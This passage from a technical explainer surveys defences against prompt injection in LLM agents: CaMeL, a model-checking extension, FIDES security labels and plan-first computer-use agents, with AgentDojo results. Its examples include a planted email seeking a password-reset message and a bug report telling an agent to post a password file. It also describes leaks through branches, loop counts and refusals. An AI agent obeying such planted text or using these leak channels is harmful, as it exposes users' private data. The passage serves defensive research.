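4. Where the program has to make sense of free text, it calls the quarantined model, which must return a value of a stated type, such as an email address.
5. The interpreter attaches a record to every value. The record lists the value's sources and its permitted readers, and a value computed from others inherits their restrictions.
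6. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs that tool's policy, a Python function that inspects the arguments and their records and then allows or denies the call.

If the program fails with an error, the planner writes a new one, which *ToolFence* (2026) names among the reasons that CaMeL is slow.

For the running example, the planner could write this program, slightly simplified:

```python
class Meeting(BaseModel):
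    is_request: bool
    title: str
    time: datetime
    guests: list[EmailStr]

for email in read_emails():
    meeting = query_quarantined_llm(
        f"Does this email propose a meeting? {email}",
        output_schema=Meeting)
    if meeting.is_request:
        create_event(title=meeting.title,
                     time=meeting.time,
                     guests=meeting.guests)
```

The first five lines declare the form of the quarantined model's answer. The rest goes through the emails one at a time and creates an event for each email that proposes a meeting. Before anything runs, a reviewer can see that the program reads the mailbox once, creates at most one event per email and sends no other messages. All the program's paths come from a single `if`, however many emails there are.

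*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls this property control-flow integrity, a term from systems security. An agent has it if its tool calls stay within a program that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information. Text from outsiders can still influence which of the program's branches runs. The stranger can write an email that makes `is_request` true or false, but can't add a new branch.

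Writing the whole program in advance also has drawbacks. The planner must know what each tool returns before it has seen a result, so Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add a full description of the output format to every tool in their tests. Most of the tasks that failed under CaMeL did so because the need for another action became clear only after a tool had returned something. If Dana's email says that the time is in an attached document, the program above has no step that opens the attachment. In other cases a tool returned data for a nearby date range instead of the one requested, and the program carried on as if nothing were wrong. (FIDES avoids some of these failures by planning one step at a time.)

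### The stranger's email inside the program

Suppose the quarantined model follows every instruction it reads, including the stranger's requests for the password-reset message and a place on every guest list.

The password-reset message isn't sent anywhere, because the quarantined model has no tools and no line of the program calls `send_email`. The instruction about invitations also fails with this particular program. Each email goes to the quarantined model in a separate call, so the model doesn't see the stranger's text when it reads Dana's proposal.

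The program does create an event for the stranger's proposal, with the stranger as guest and a title and time the stranger chose. This follows the user's request literally. The user gets an unwanted calendar entry, but the stranger learns nothing new from the invitation.

A slightly different program would depend on the policy for its safety. The planner could have put all ten emails into one prompt, in which case the quarantined model might return Dana's budget meeting with both Dana and the stranger as guests. A policy for `create_event` could prevent the leak by comparing the guests with the permitted readers:

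```python
def create_event_policy(args):
    for guest in args.guests:
        if guest not in readers(args.title, args.time):
            return Denied("Guest may not read these details")
    return Allowed()
```

| Program | Permitted readers of Dana's meeting details | Stranger as guest | Dana as guest |
|---|---|---|---|
| One email per prompt | The user and Dana | Denied | Allowed |
| All emails in one prompt | Only the user | Denied | Denied |

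In the second row, the interpreter has to treat the title and time as dependent on all ten emails, and only the user may read all ten. The stranger gets no invitation in either case, but the planner's choice of prompt determines whether Dana gets hers.

A policy could check where a value came from instead of who may read it. Willison's example allows `send_email` only if the recipient is trusted, and otherwise the system can ask the user to approve the message. In the calendar task it would ask about Dana too, just as PACT would reject her address. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) found the same problem in *The LLMbda Calculus* when they rebuilt CaMeL's design in a small formal language. In their example an injection could not alter the message's subject or body, but the recipient's address remained untrusted, even though it was correct, because the quarantined model had extracted it from an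 email.

These records also make it easier to find the cause of an action. CaMeL's interpreter keeps a graph that links each argument to the values it was derived from, and an ordinary agent's log lacks these links. If each prompt contains only one email, a reviewer can trace a suspicious guest to a single message.

### Two meanings of "capability"

The CaMeL paper calls these records capabilities, but the word usually means something different in operating systems. The usual meaning goes back to Dennis and Van Horn, who in 1966 described a capability as something a running program holds that identifies an object, such as a file, and specifies what the program may do with it. A program without a capability for a file cannot use that file.

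A capability in CaMeL is metadata attached to a value, and it doesn't grant any permissions. It records where the value came from and who may read it, and CaMeL checks it against a policy before a tool call uses the value. For example, a policy may allow a guest list from an untrusted source in a private draft but not in an invitation.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) uses "capability" in the older sense. Its "capability monitor" keeps a list of the tools an agent holds and can withdraw some of them when the agent first reads untrusted text. Under stated assumptions, including that each injected instruction makes a single tool call, Dongol proves that withdrawing every tool an injection could call prevents it from causing any leak beyond those the plan itself causes. CaMeL instead leaves the tools in place and allows or blocks each call based on the values in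 it.

### What the records miss

Dongol also tested small formal versions of the two-model design in Isabelle/HOL, a program that checks mathematical proofs. In these versions, the attacker may choose any answer for the quarantined model, including one that depends on the user's private notes. The versions are test cases for a definition of security, not CaMeL's actual code.

| Design | Result |
|---|---|
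| No records on values | Leaks, because the quarantined model can copy the notes into an answer that the plan sends |
| Records, with a ban on sending private values to outsiders | Secure for every answer, but also blocks the honest reply |
| The same, but outsiders can see the refused requests | Leaks when a refusal shows the contents of the request |
| Records that follow values but not conditions | Leaks through the choice of branch |

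The last row needs an example. Suppose a plan contains these lines:

```python
reply = "No"
if "merger" in notes:
    reply = "Yes"
send_email(recipient=stranger, body=reply)
```

The planner wrote both "Yes" and "No", so neither word comes from a private source, and each passes a check that covers only the value's source. The stranger still learns from the answer whether the notes mention a merger. CaMeL's STRICT mode also records the conditions on which a value depends. Dongol notes that this mode is meant to prevent the leak but leaves the proof to future work.

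Even an interpreter that tracks conditions can miss a dependency. If the notes do not mention a merger, the third line never runs, and the interpreter may leave `reply` with its original record, although "No" reveals just as much as "Yes". Peters-Gill and colleagues, citing Garby and colleagues, confirm that CaMeL's interpreter can miss such dependencies. They add that CaMeL's retries after a failure can leak information, because whether a policy refuses a call may depend on private data.

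Information can also escape through the number of calls. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) describes a loop that fetches a harmless page as many times as the value of a secret number. Whoever runs the page's server can learn the number by counting the visits.

These leaks require a plan with a suitable branch or loop, and the attacker does not write the plan. The guarantee still depends on trusting the interpreter, the policies, the code that assigns records to tool results, and the user's request. If the user pastes a stranger's text into the request, the planner treats it as an instruction. Peters-Gill and colleagues show that a similar problem arises when CaMeL agents work together. One agent can include an outsider's text in its request to another, whose planner then treats the text as trusted. They prevent this by sending such text through a separate channel that the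 second planner cannot read.

### Checking a plan before it runs

CaMeL checks each call separately, just before it runs. A plan may therefore run for an hour before a policy blocks its last step. Separate checks also cannot enforce a rule such as "if the agent opens an incident ticket, it must eventually close it", because opening the ticket is harmless and the violation is never making the later call to close it.

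But a CaMeL plan is a short program, and the planner has finished writing it before any tool runs. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, take advantage of this with a model checker, a tool that searches all the states a system can reach for one that breaks a rule. Their system, which they published in September 2026, works between the planner and the interpreter:

1. It parses the plan and finds the tool calls, assignments, branches and loops.
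2. It builds a finite-state machine with a state for each point in the program and a transition for each possible next step.
3. It marks each variable's origin as trusted, user, untrusted or quarantined model, in that order. A value computed from several others takes the least trusted origin among them.
4. It passes the machine and the relevant rules to a model checker called nuXmv.
5. If every rule holds, CaMeL runs the plan with its usual policies. If one fails, the planner receives a description of the failure and tries to repair the plan, up to a set number of times.

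The rules use temporal logic, which adds statements about order and time to ordinary logic. Four forms cover most of them:

| Formula | Meaning |
|---|---|
| AG p | p holds in every state on every path |
| AF p | every path eventually reaches a state where p holds |
| EF p | at least one path reaches a state where p holds |
| A[p U q] | on every path, p holds until q becomes true, and q does become true |

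One of their worked examples is a plan that sends Bob a message, here with slightly different wording:

```python
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
address = query_quarantined_llm(
    f"Find Bob's address: {messages}", EmailStr)
send_direct_message(address, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

The rule is that the agent must never send a direct message to a recipient from an untrusted source:

AG(call_send_direct_message ⇒ recipient_trusted)

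The plan has no branches, so the machine is a chain of five states.

| State | Step | What the checker knows |
|---|---|---|
| Start | None | No tool has run |
| s0 | Read the channel | `messages` is untrusted |
| s1 | Extract the address | `address` comes from the quarantined model, so it is tainted |
| s2 | Send the message | The call happens, and its recipient is tainted |
| Done | None | The plan has ended |

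The rule fails if any reachable state has the call without a trusted recipient. State s2 does, so nuXmv reports that the formula is false and prints a counterexample, the sequence of states from the start to s2. In s2, `send_direct_message_called` and `recipient_tainted` are both true. The software turns the counterexample into an explanation for the planner. No tool has run yet, so the explanation cannot contain text from an outsider.

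If the user's request includes Bob's address, the planner can write it into the program, because constants in the program count as trusted. If the request does not include it, this rule would not stop the planner from inventing one. An attacker could not have chosen the invented address, but the message might go to the wrong person.

A similar rule for guests would reject every version of the calendar plan, since the guests always come from emails. A developer could instead require approval first:

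A[¬call_create_event U ask_user_called]

A plan satisfies this rule if it asks the user before creating the first event, even if it then creates ten events without asking again, because the formula restricts only what happens before the first request for approval. The checker proves only that the plan satisfies the formula, so someone has to read the formula as carefully as the plan.

### How much the checker could prove

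Nikolaou and colleagues first tried to express CaMeL's existing policies for the AgentDojo benchmark as temporal rules. They could check 22 of the 28 policies in advance: all 5 for banking, all 6 for travel, 8 of 10 for office work and 3 of 7 for Slack. The other six depend on facts that exist only while the plan runs, such as who can currently read a shared file.

They then ran all 97 AgentDojo tasks with Claude Haiku 4.5, both under CaMeL's run-time checks and under their advance checks. A plan passed if the system allowed it and it did what the user wanted.

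| Result | Tasks |
|---|---|
| Passed under both | 42 |
| Allowed under both but did not do the task | 22 |
| Blocked under both | 17 |
| Passed only with the advance check | 9 |
| Passed only with CaMeL's run-time check | 7 |

CaMeL and CaMeLoT agreed on 59 of 75 plans, excluding 22 that did not do the task. Most disagreements arose because CaMeL used run-time facts that were unavailable to CaMeLoT's advance check. Six of the seven tasks that only CaMeL passed were office tasks, where the trustworthiness of most tool results depends on run-time details, such as who wrote a calendar entry. CaMeLoT treats such results as tainted, which probably explains why it blocked these plans. The test had no injected instructions, so it measured agreement between the two checks, not resistance to attack. For the same reason, all 17 tasks that both systems blocked were legitimate user requests.

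A second experiment used rules that CaMeL's policies do not naturally express. In a simulated security team, an agent investigates an alert and may isolate an infected computer by cutting it off from the network. In the safe plan, the agent confirms which computer is affected, opens a ticket, requests approval, isolates the computer and closes the ticket. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven unsafe versions of this plan by hand.

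| Fault in the plan | Advance check | Simplified CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| Isolates the computer before confirming which one is affected | Caught | Missed |
| Isolates it without requesting approval | Caught | Missed |
| Never isolates it | Caught | Missed |
| Opens a ticket and never closes or escalates it | Caught | Missed |
| Isolates it immediately after scanning attachments | Caught | Missed |
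| Takes strong action before opening a ticket | Caught | Missed |
| Blocks a network address that came from the quarantined model | Caught | Caught |

The result of seven against one is less impressive than it looks because the simplified CaMeL tracked only whether values were tainted, and Nikolaou and colleagues chose the rules to go beyond that. A run-time monitor that remembered earlier calls could catch several of these faults, such as isolation without a request for approval. But it could not establish in advance that the agent will close a ticket later, so a check on the whole plan has a clear advantage there.

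The planner also produced unsafe plans when the user's request led it to. One user said time was short and told the agent to skip the approval. In four such tests, the advance check caught every bad plan and the simplified CaMeL caught none. CaMeL's separation of models offers no protection here because the unsafe instruction came from the user, whom the planner is supposed to obey.

### Loops, run-time facts and written rules

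The checker can reject safe plans because it ignores the conditions in branches and loops. At each `if` it considers both branches, and at each loop it considers both another round and an exit. Consider a plan with two separate tests of the same condition:

```python
if important:
    confirm_host(name)
if important:
    isolate_host(name)
```

The plan never isolates a computer without confirming it first, but the checker also explores a path that skips the first branch and takes the second, so it reports a violation. Similarly, AF(call_create_event) fails for the calendar plan even if the mailbox always contains a proposal, because the checker includes a path where the loop ends at once. This approximation keeps the number of states finite without leaving out dangerous paths, but it produces false alarms. Nikolaou and colleagues consider that acceptable because a false alarm usually leads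 to one repair attempt, before any tool has run.

The checker cannot inspect what happens inside a tool. The safe plan for the security team calls `request_ir_approval` and isolates the computer in the next line without testing the answer, because the rule requires only that the request come first. If the tool returns "refused" instead of stopping the plan, the verified plan still isolates the computer. The checker also cannot confirm that the quarantined model has identified the right computer.

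Someone also has to write CaMeL's rules. For AgentDojo's four simulated settings, it needs a policy for each of the 28 functions with side effects and rules for marking the results of 46 others. Nikolaou and colleagues let a model derive extra rules from each user's request. The model chooses from ten kinds of obligation, such as "a before b", and ordinary code turns them into formulas and rejects any that name an unknown tool. Every rule proposed this way was well formed. When GPT-4.1 nano wrote formulas directly, 85 of the 97 tasks had at least one invalid formula.

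Some of the well-formed rules were still wrong. Claude Haiku 4.5 identified exactly the right actions with side effects in 85 of the 97 tasks, or 88 if conditional actions count. In the other nine, the checker would have enforced a misreading of the request.

Willison doubts that ordinary users can write such policies. After two decades of working on application security, he still finds Amazon's access permissions system difficult. Asking the user to decide uncertain cases brings back the risk that they will approve actions out of habit.

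## How FIDES tracks security labels through an agent

FIDES, which Microsoft researchers published in May 2025, lets the planner choose one step at a time, as an ordinary agent does, but restricts what the planner sees between steps. Unlike CaMeL, it doesn't fix the whole plan in advance, so a reviewer has no finished program to read beforehand. The protection comes from security labels that ordinary code attaches to every value and checks before each tool call. Security researchers call this method information-flow control, and Dorothy Denning formalized it mathematically in 1976.

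### Labels and the join

FIDES gives each value an integrity label and a confidentiality label. The integrity label is either trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and the confidentiality label is the set of people who may read the value. Labels have an order, written ⊑, in which a higher label puts more limits on what software may do with the value. So T ⊑ U, and a set of readers ranks above any larger set that contains it.

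A value that depends on several others gets the join of their labels, written ⊔. The join is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as each of them. For integrity, one untrusted input is enough to make the result untrusted:

T ⊔ T = T, T ⊔ U = U, U ⊔ U = U

For confidentiality, the join is the intersection of the two sets, because only people who may read both inputs may read something derived from both:

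{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

In the running example, the labels could be:

| Value | Integrity | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Trusted | Everyone |
| Dana's email | Untrusted | The user, Dana |
| The stranger's email | Untrusted | The user, the stranger |
| A summary of both emails | Untrusted | Only the user |

The same calculation can prevent a leak when nobody is attacking. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a user, Alex, who asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't yet allowed to see the figures, has written to ask about them. Once the agent has read both emails, anything it writes carries the label {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the software will not send it to Marco without asking Alex. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the label would be {Alex,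 Marco} and the reply could go out.

Tools supply the labels and can attach one to a whole result or to each field in it. Costa and colleagues treat an email's sender and recipients as its readers, although someone may have shared it more widely. Parts of an email can differ in integrity. For example, mail servers can authenticate a sender's address, so a system could label that field trusted and the body untrusted.

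### How the loop hides results

The simplest approach is to keep one label for the planner's whole history and update it with every message. Nobody can tell which parts of its input a language model used, so each new tool call inherits the joined label of everything the model has read. This is safe but severely limits the agent. After `read_emails`, the history is untrusted, so a rule that allows important actions only when the history is trusted will block `create_event` for the rest of the run. Costa and colleagues also built this version as a baseline, which they call the basic planner.

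FIDES keeps the history trusted for longer by hiding results from the planner:

1. The software puts the user's request into the history with the label "trusted, readable by everyone".
2. The planner reads the history and requests a tool call. It can give a variable's name as an argument in place of a value.
3. The software replaces each name with the stored value, which keeps its own label.
4. The software checks the call against the tool's policy. If the call fails, the planner receives a message about the violation and can try something else.
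5. The tool runs, and its result gets the join of the labels of the call, the arguments and any stored data that the tool read.
6. The software compares each part of the result with the label of the history. It stores any part with a more restrictive label in a new variable and shows the planner only the name. The other parts go into the history as they are.
7. The loop returns to step 2.

Step 3 allows a trusted call to carry untrusted content. If the user asks the agent to send the three latest emails to Sam on Slack, the planner can write `send_message(to="Sam", message=#read_emails_0)` without seeing the contents of the emails. The choice of tool and recipient depends only on the user's request, and the policy can require both to be trusted while accepting an untrusted message.

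Two more tools let the planner use hidden text. `query_llm` sends a question and some variables to a quarantined model and stores the answer in another variable, labelled with the join of its inputs' labels. `inspect` reveals a variable's content to the planner, and the history then takes on that content's label. The planner can therefore read a whole email if it must, which CaMeL never allows, but afterwards it may no longer be permitted to act.

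### Trusted action and permitted flow

FIDES relies on two basic policies, which *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) calls trusted action and permitted flow.

Trusted action allows a call only if the planner decided on it with a trusted history. A policy can also require particular arguments to be trusted. Permitted flow applies to calls that send data somewhere. If the data has the permitted readers S and the call would deliver it to the recipients R, the call may run only if every recipient is a permitted reader:

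R ⊆ S

Permitted flow alone does not stop a prompt injection. The stranger could still cause the agent to send an email, but only with content its recipients were already allowed to read. Trusted action alone lets data reach new readers, assuming that a release the agent decides on from a trusted history is what the user wanted. Security researchers call this robust declassification.

In their experiments, Costa and colleagues chose which policies each tool call must satisfy. Sending money or deleting an email requires a trusted action. Sending an email or creating a calendar event must satisfy at least one of the two policies, and adding guests to an existing event must satisfy both. They also extended permitted flow to block messages that contain an untrusted link, because opening a link can send data to whoever runs the website.

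### Data-independent and data-dependent tasks

How much a planner can do without looking at results depends on the task. A task is data independent if one fixed sequence of tool calls, followed by one fixed response, solves it for every possible state of the data. Formally, let t(d) be the set of action sequences that solve task t when the stored data is d. The task is data independent if at least one sequence belongs to t(d) for every possible d. Otherwise it is data dependent.

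Sending Sam three emails from a mailbox is data independent because the same two calls work for any mailbox. Sending him a summary of those emails is also data independent if the planner can use a quarantined model to write the summary and then pass it on by variable name.

The running example, which closely matches one from Costa and colleagues, is data dependent because the agent needs to call `create_event` only if the mailbox contains a proposal. A planner that never sees any result therefore cannot solve the task unless it writes this condition into a program in advance, as in CaMeL.

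### Showing the planner one bit

In FIDES the planner has to learn whether there is a meeting request, but it doesn't have to read the emails to find out. It can ask for an answer that must be true or false, and look only at that:

| Step | Planner's call | What the planner then sees |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `read_emails()` | The name `#emails` |
| 2 | `query_llm("Does an email ask for a meeting?", #emails, bool)` | The name `#answer` |
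| 3 | `inspect(#answer)` | `true` |
| 4 | `query_llm("Extract the event details", #emails, event)` | The name `#event` |
| 5 | `create_event(#event)` | A confirmation |

Strictly, the history is untrusted after step 3, because the answer came from emails that outsiders wrote. But an injected instruction needs room for words, and a true-or-false answer has none. FIDES therefore adds the type of a value to its label and orders types by how much information they can carry:

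bool ⊑ enum["a", "b", "c"] ⊑ string

A Boolean carries one bit, an enumeration (a choice from a fixed list) of n options carries at most log₂ n bits, or about 1.6 bits for three options, and a string has no limit. A policy can therefore accept an untrusted Boolean where it would refuse an untrusted string. It can likewise release a single bit of secret data. Constrained decoding ensures that the quarantined model's answer has the declared type.

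An enumeration gives the planner more information. If the options were "time in the email", "time in an attachment" and "no time given", the planner could open Dana's attachment if it got the second answer. The CaMeL program in the previous section had no step for this.

The type label limits each answer but not the number of answers. The join of bool with bool is still bool, so a history with ten such answers can carry the same type label as a history with one. If the planner asks ten yes-or-no questions about the whole mailbox, a stranger who controls the quarantined model's answers can choose any of 2^10 = 1,024 combinations. The stranger can still only steer the planner among actions it would consider anyway, but with up to ten bits of influence instead of one.

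### The stranger's email under each policy

Suppose again that the quarantined model follows every instruction in the stranger's email. As in CaMeL, the password-reset message stays where it is. But the stranger can still make the answer in step 2 false despite the labels, and the agent will then skip Dana's meeting.

Whether the stranger can join Dana's meeting depends on the policy for `create_event`. The first two rows below apply if the policy accepts the true-or-false answer as safe.

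| Policy | Dana and the stranger as guests | Dana alone |
|---|---|---|
| Trusted action, checking only the call | Runs | Runs |
| Trusted action, checking the guests too | Blocked | Blocked |
| Permitted flow, details taken from all emails | Blocked | Blocked |
| Permitted flow, details taken from Dana's email | Blocked | Runs |

The "either policy" rule from the experiments would let the altered guest list through. The planner was right to create an event, the check on the call covers only that decision, and the software assumes the user wants the details released. Requiring both policies, as the experiments did for adding guests to an existing event, would block the stranger's invitation. Dana would then get hers only if the planner had queried her email separately, so the planner's choice of query matters here as it did in CaMeL.

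Another solution is to use authenticated sender addresses. If the sender field is trusted, the planner can read it, ask the quarantined model whether each email proposes the meeting, and invite the sender of the one that does. The guest list then contains no value that the quarantined model produced, but it omits anyone Dana mentioned only in the text.

### Explicit secrecy and what it leaves out

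The confidentiality guarantee that Costa and colleagues claim for this kind of label tracking is called explicit secrecy. Divide the stored data into public and secret parts, and let d₁ be the data at the start of a run. The tool calls in that run, with their arguments held fixed, act on the data as a function g. The run satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every d₂ with the same public part as d₁,

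g(d₁) and g(d₂) have the same public part.

If someone replayed the same calls on data with different secrets, outsiders would see no difference. A call that forwards email number 3 to the stranger fails this test when that email is secret, because replaying it with a different email would send different text. A call that sends the stranger a fixed word passes.

The definition doesn't cover why the agent made those calls and not others, so it permits leaks like the one in the merger example, where the choice of branch revealed what the notes contained. Not receiving an invitation can reveal information in the same way. The guarantee also excludes side channels such as timing and network packet size.

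A stronger property, non-interference, would close the first of these gaps. It requires that changing secret data never affects anything an outsider can observe, including which calls the agent makes. Costa and colleagues rejected it as too restrictive, because in practice it would forbid any call with publicly visible effects after any call that might have read a secret. A calendar agent has to read the mailbox first, so it could never send an invitation. Web browsers and TaintDroid, a system that tracks private data on Android phones, make the same compromise.

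*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) is stricter. Its planner writes a complete plan in a small language, and every step inside a branch inherits the label of the branch's condition. On AgentDojo, switching on the label checks reduced successful attacks from 0.4% to zero but cut completed tasks from 53.0% to 29.0%. Not all of that loss comes from tracking conditions. About half the runs stopped at the label check, typically because a plan passed untrusted tool output to a tool that required trusted input, which SPA would reject even without branches. Still, if the calendar tool required trusted input, SPA would reject the running example, since whether the event is created depends on an outsider's email.

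### Attacks on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks and 36 attack goals, running everything five times. The simulated attacker knows the agent's tools and plants instructions to call them. They used OpenAI's GPT-4o, released in May 2024, as both the planner and the quarantined model, then repeated the utility tests with o1, a reasoning model from December 2024.

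| Planner (GPT-4o) | Successful injections without policy checks | With policy checks |
|---|---|---|
| Basic | 152 | 0 |
| Variable passing (can never look inside a variable) | 0 | 0 |
| FIDES | 21 | 0 |

Without policy checks, FIDES let the 21 attacks through because it may reveal an untrusted variable to the planner and then continue as normal. A simpler defence, in which a model removes the tools a task doesn't need before the agent starts, let through 20. Both numbers come from one fixed style of attack, and an attacker who adapted to the defence could probably do better. The zeros in the last column are more robust because a rule prevents an untrusted history from triggering certain calls, however persuasive the injected text is. This protection depends on correct labels and policies.

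These are the counts after manual review. AgentDojo's own scoring reported 3 successful attacks against FIDES with checks on and 20 against the basic planner. Some were calls that the policy had blocked but the benchmark counted as made. Others were actions that the policy permits, such as creating a calendar event with no guests. A third group changed only the agent's words, such as when an injected instruction made it recommend a particular place to visit. FIDES does not try to prevent these attacks, so a user can still read a summary that an outsider has influenced. The text keeps its untrusted label, which an application could show to the user.

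### Tasks completed

In the paper's headline result, FIDES with GPT-4o completes 8% more tasks than a basic planner under the same policies. An agent with no protection completes far more tasks than either. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed when there is no attack, and the last column is a simple average of the four settings.

| Model and planner | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
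|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, basic, no policies | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 84.3 |
| GPT-4o, basic, with policies | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 41.9 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES, with policies | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 50.0 |
| o1, basic, no policies | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 | 84.0 |
| o1, basic, with policies | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 | 44.4 |
| o1, FIDES, with policies | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 | 60.8 |

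With GPT-4o, FIDES is about 8 percentage points ahead of the basic planner under the same policies and about 34 points behind the unprotected agent. With o1, it is about 16 points ahead and 23 behind. Travel is the exception. Many of its tools may run with an untrusted history as long as no private data leaks, so the policies barely restrict the basic planner, but FIDES still has to work with variables.

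Costa and colleagues also tested FIDES with the policy checks switched off, to measure how much the variables and extra queries alone reduced task completion. FIDES completed 23.7 percentage points fewer tasks than the basic planner with GPT-4o, and 6.3 points fewer with o1. The paper's introduction gives only the 6.3-point figure and does not name the model. GPT-4o could write correct queries to the quarantined model, but not consistently, and it sometimes confused variable names. o1, released seven months later, avoided most of the loss by planning better.

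The remaining loss comes partly from the policies working as intended. The researchers classify about a fifth of the tasks as data dependent, including 44% of banking tasks and 43% of Slack tasks. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policy forbids when the file is untrusted. Planners also made avoidable mistakes. In one Slack task, the planner fetched the list of channels although the user had named the channel, which needlessly made the planner's history untrusted.

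Some tasks were completed partly by luck. All the travel tasks require reading hidden text, which the variable-passing planner cannot do, but with the checks off it still completed 43% of them with GPT-4o and 2% with o1. In some cases it recommended the right hotel without seeing the ratings. In a banking task, the user asked the agent to change the password if there was a suspicious transaction. The planner could see the amounts and dates but not the descriptions, which were untrusted. It judged a large payment suspicious and changed the password without checking the descriptions, the evidence most likely to settle the question. No outsider influenced that decision, so the change violated no policy.

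Costa and colleagues also left constrained decoding, which they found unnecessary for most of the tasks, out of the experiments. The AgentDojo results therefore provide little evidence about whether a policy can safely trust a one-bit answer, the part of the design that matters most for the running example.

### Later tests and Microsoft's release

Two later studies support the main pattern, in which the policies supply the security and hiding results in variables recovers part of the lost utility. Kolluri and colleagues, who include several of the FIDES researchers, reran FIDES on AgentDojo with newer reasoning models. With o3-mini, from January 2025, it completed 50.1% of the tasks without any human approval, compared with 35.5% for the basic planner under the same policies. PRUDENTIA, the successor they propose, also tells the planner which labels and policies apply. *Formal Policy Enforcement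 for Agentic Systems* (2026) applied FIDES's policies to AgentDojo's standard GPT-4o agent, which does not hide results in variables. This reduced successful attacks from 25.2% of runs to 1.0%, not counting blocked calls, but it also reduced the share of tasks completed from 79.0% to 32.2%. The few attacks that still succeeded concerned the wording of the final reply.

In May 2026, Microsoft added FIDES to its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, as an experimental feature. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) works through an attack on an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub, a site where developers share code. A public report contains a hidden instruction to read a file of passwords and post its contents as a comment. In this set-up the planner reads the report directly, and the software tracks the labels:

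| Event | Label of the history afterwards |
|---|---|
| The agent reads the bug report | Untrusted, public |
| The agent obeys and reads the password file, which is trusted and private | Untrusted, private |
| The agent tries to post a public comment | The software blocks the call or asks the user |

The attack fails even though the model was fooled. By default, the framework also hides untrusted results, so the planner would not see the instruction.

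The release depends on developers labelling their data sources. A tool without a label counts as trusted and public, and Microsoft is asking users whether the default should be the opposite. In the running example, if a developer forgot to label `read_emails`, the planner would see the stranger's email directly, its history would still count as trusted, and every integrity check would pass. Labels also accumulate over a run until they block legitimate work, which Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) call label creep in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*.

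FIDES erases the labels when the run ends, as *MemLineage* (2026) points out, and this matters for agents with lasting memory. Girrens and Wang describe a user who asks an agent on Monday to save an invoice's details, and on Tuesday to pay it. If an attacker wrote the account number on the invoice and the agent saved it without its label, nothing on Tuesday would mark the number as untrusted. SPA stores each saved result with its label and restores both when a later plan retrieves the result.

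## Planning a computer task before seeing the screen

CaMeL and FIDES both rely on tools with fixed meanings, so when a program calls `create_event`, the developer knows beforehand what kind of action it will take. A computer-use agent has no such tools. It looks at a screenshot and then moves the mouse, clicks and types, so it can work with almost any application that a person can use. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) tests whether a planner can still write the whole program before any model looks at the screen.

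### Why clicking seems to need constant observation

The effect of `click(412, 230)` depends on what is on the screen. As Piet, Chow and colleagues (2026) point out in *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm*, a click at the same coordinates can open a product on one page and buy or delete something on another. Later actions may also become visible only after earlier ones are taken. Most computer-use agents therefore take a new screenshot after every action and use it to choose the next one, so any text on the screen could redirect them.

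A user's request also gives little information about the starting point. The browser may be closed, open on the wrong site, or covered by a cookie notice. In one test task, the user asks the agent to "browse the natural products database" while the browser shows drugs.com. The site has no obvious button for this. The right route goes through a page on drugs and medications to a list of categories. Foerster and colleagues say that even people might need several tries to find it.

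*AI Planning Framework for LLM-Based Web Agents* (2026) recommends planning the whole task in advance for highly structured sites such as online shops, and observing repeatedly where the agent must check a system's state before each click. The new design relies on the assumption that the possible states at each step are predictable enough for a planner to write a branch for each, even though nobody could list every possible screen.

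### Observe, verify, act

The design keeps CaMeL's planner and interpreter. The quarantined model is now a perception model, which reads screenshots and the page's underlying structure. The planner writes its program as a series of three-part steps:

1. Observe: the program asks the perception model to describe the screen.
2. Verify: the program calls `verify_hypothesis`, in which a quarantined model compares that description with a condition the planner predicted and answers OK, FAIL or UNKNOWN.
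3. Act: the interpreter follows the branch for that answer, and the program clicks or types.

For the calendar request, the plan could begin like this, slightly simplified:

```python
screen = summarize_screenshot("Which program or site is open?")
inbox = verify_hypothesis(screen, "A webmail inbox is open")
if inbox != "OK":
    link = find("a tab or bookmark that opens the user's webmail")
    if link is not None:
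        click(link)
    else:
        hotkey("CTRL+L")
        type_text("mail.example.com\n")
```

`find` gets the coordinates of whatever matches the description from the perception model. The interpreter passes them to `click`, and the planner never sees them. These nine lines have three possible execution paths, and at best they only get the agent to the inbox. CaMeL's program for the same request reached the inbox and read the messages with a single call, `read_emails()`.

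Foerster and colleagues derived the pattern from plans that had worked. They also instructed the planner on common situations, such as how to dismiss a cookie notice, what to do after a failed click, and when to try a different description of a button. On 60 tasks, a planner with these instructions and `verify_hypothesis` solved 25 at the first attempt, compared with 4 for a planner with a generic prompt.

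### How large the plans become

The researchers compared these plans with CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo, where every tool has a name and a defined result. The table gives averages per plan.

| | AgentDojo | Computer use, generic prompt | Computer use, observe–verify–act |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 52 | 72 | 213 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 19.8 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 11.3 | 39.7 |
| Overlap between plans for the same task (1 = same routes) | 0.39 | 0.001 | 0.04 |

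About half of the steps in a computer-use plan are fallbacks that do not execute on any given run. In the longest computer-use plans, 9% of the branch conditions use only values inside the plan, such as a loop counter, compared with 79% in AgentDojo. About 24 of the 40 branches in those longest plans depend on a model's output about the screen.

### What a reader gains from the plan

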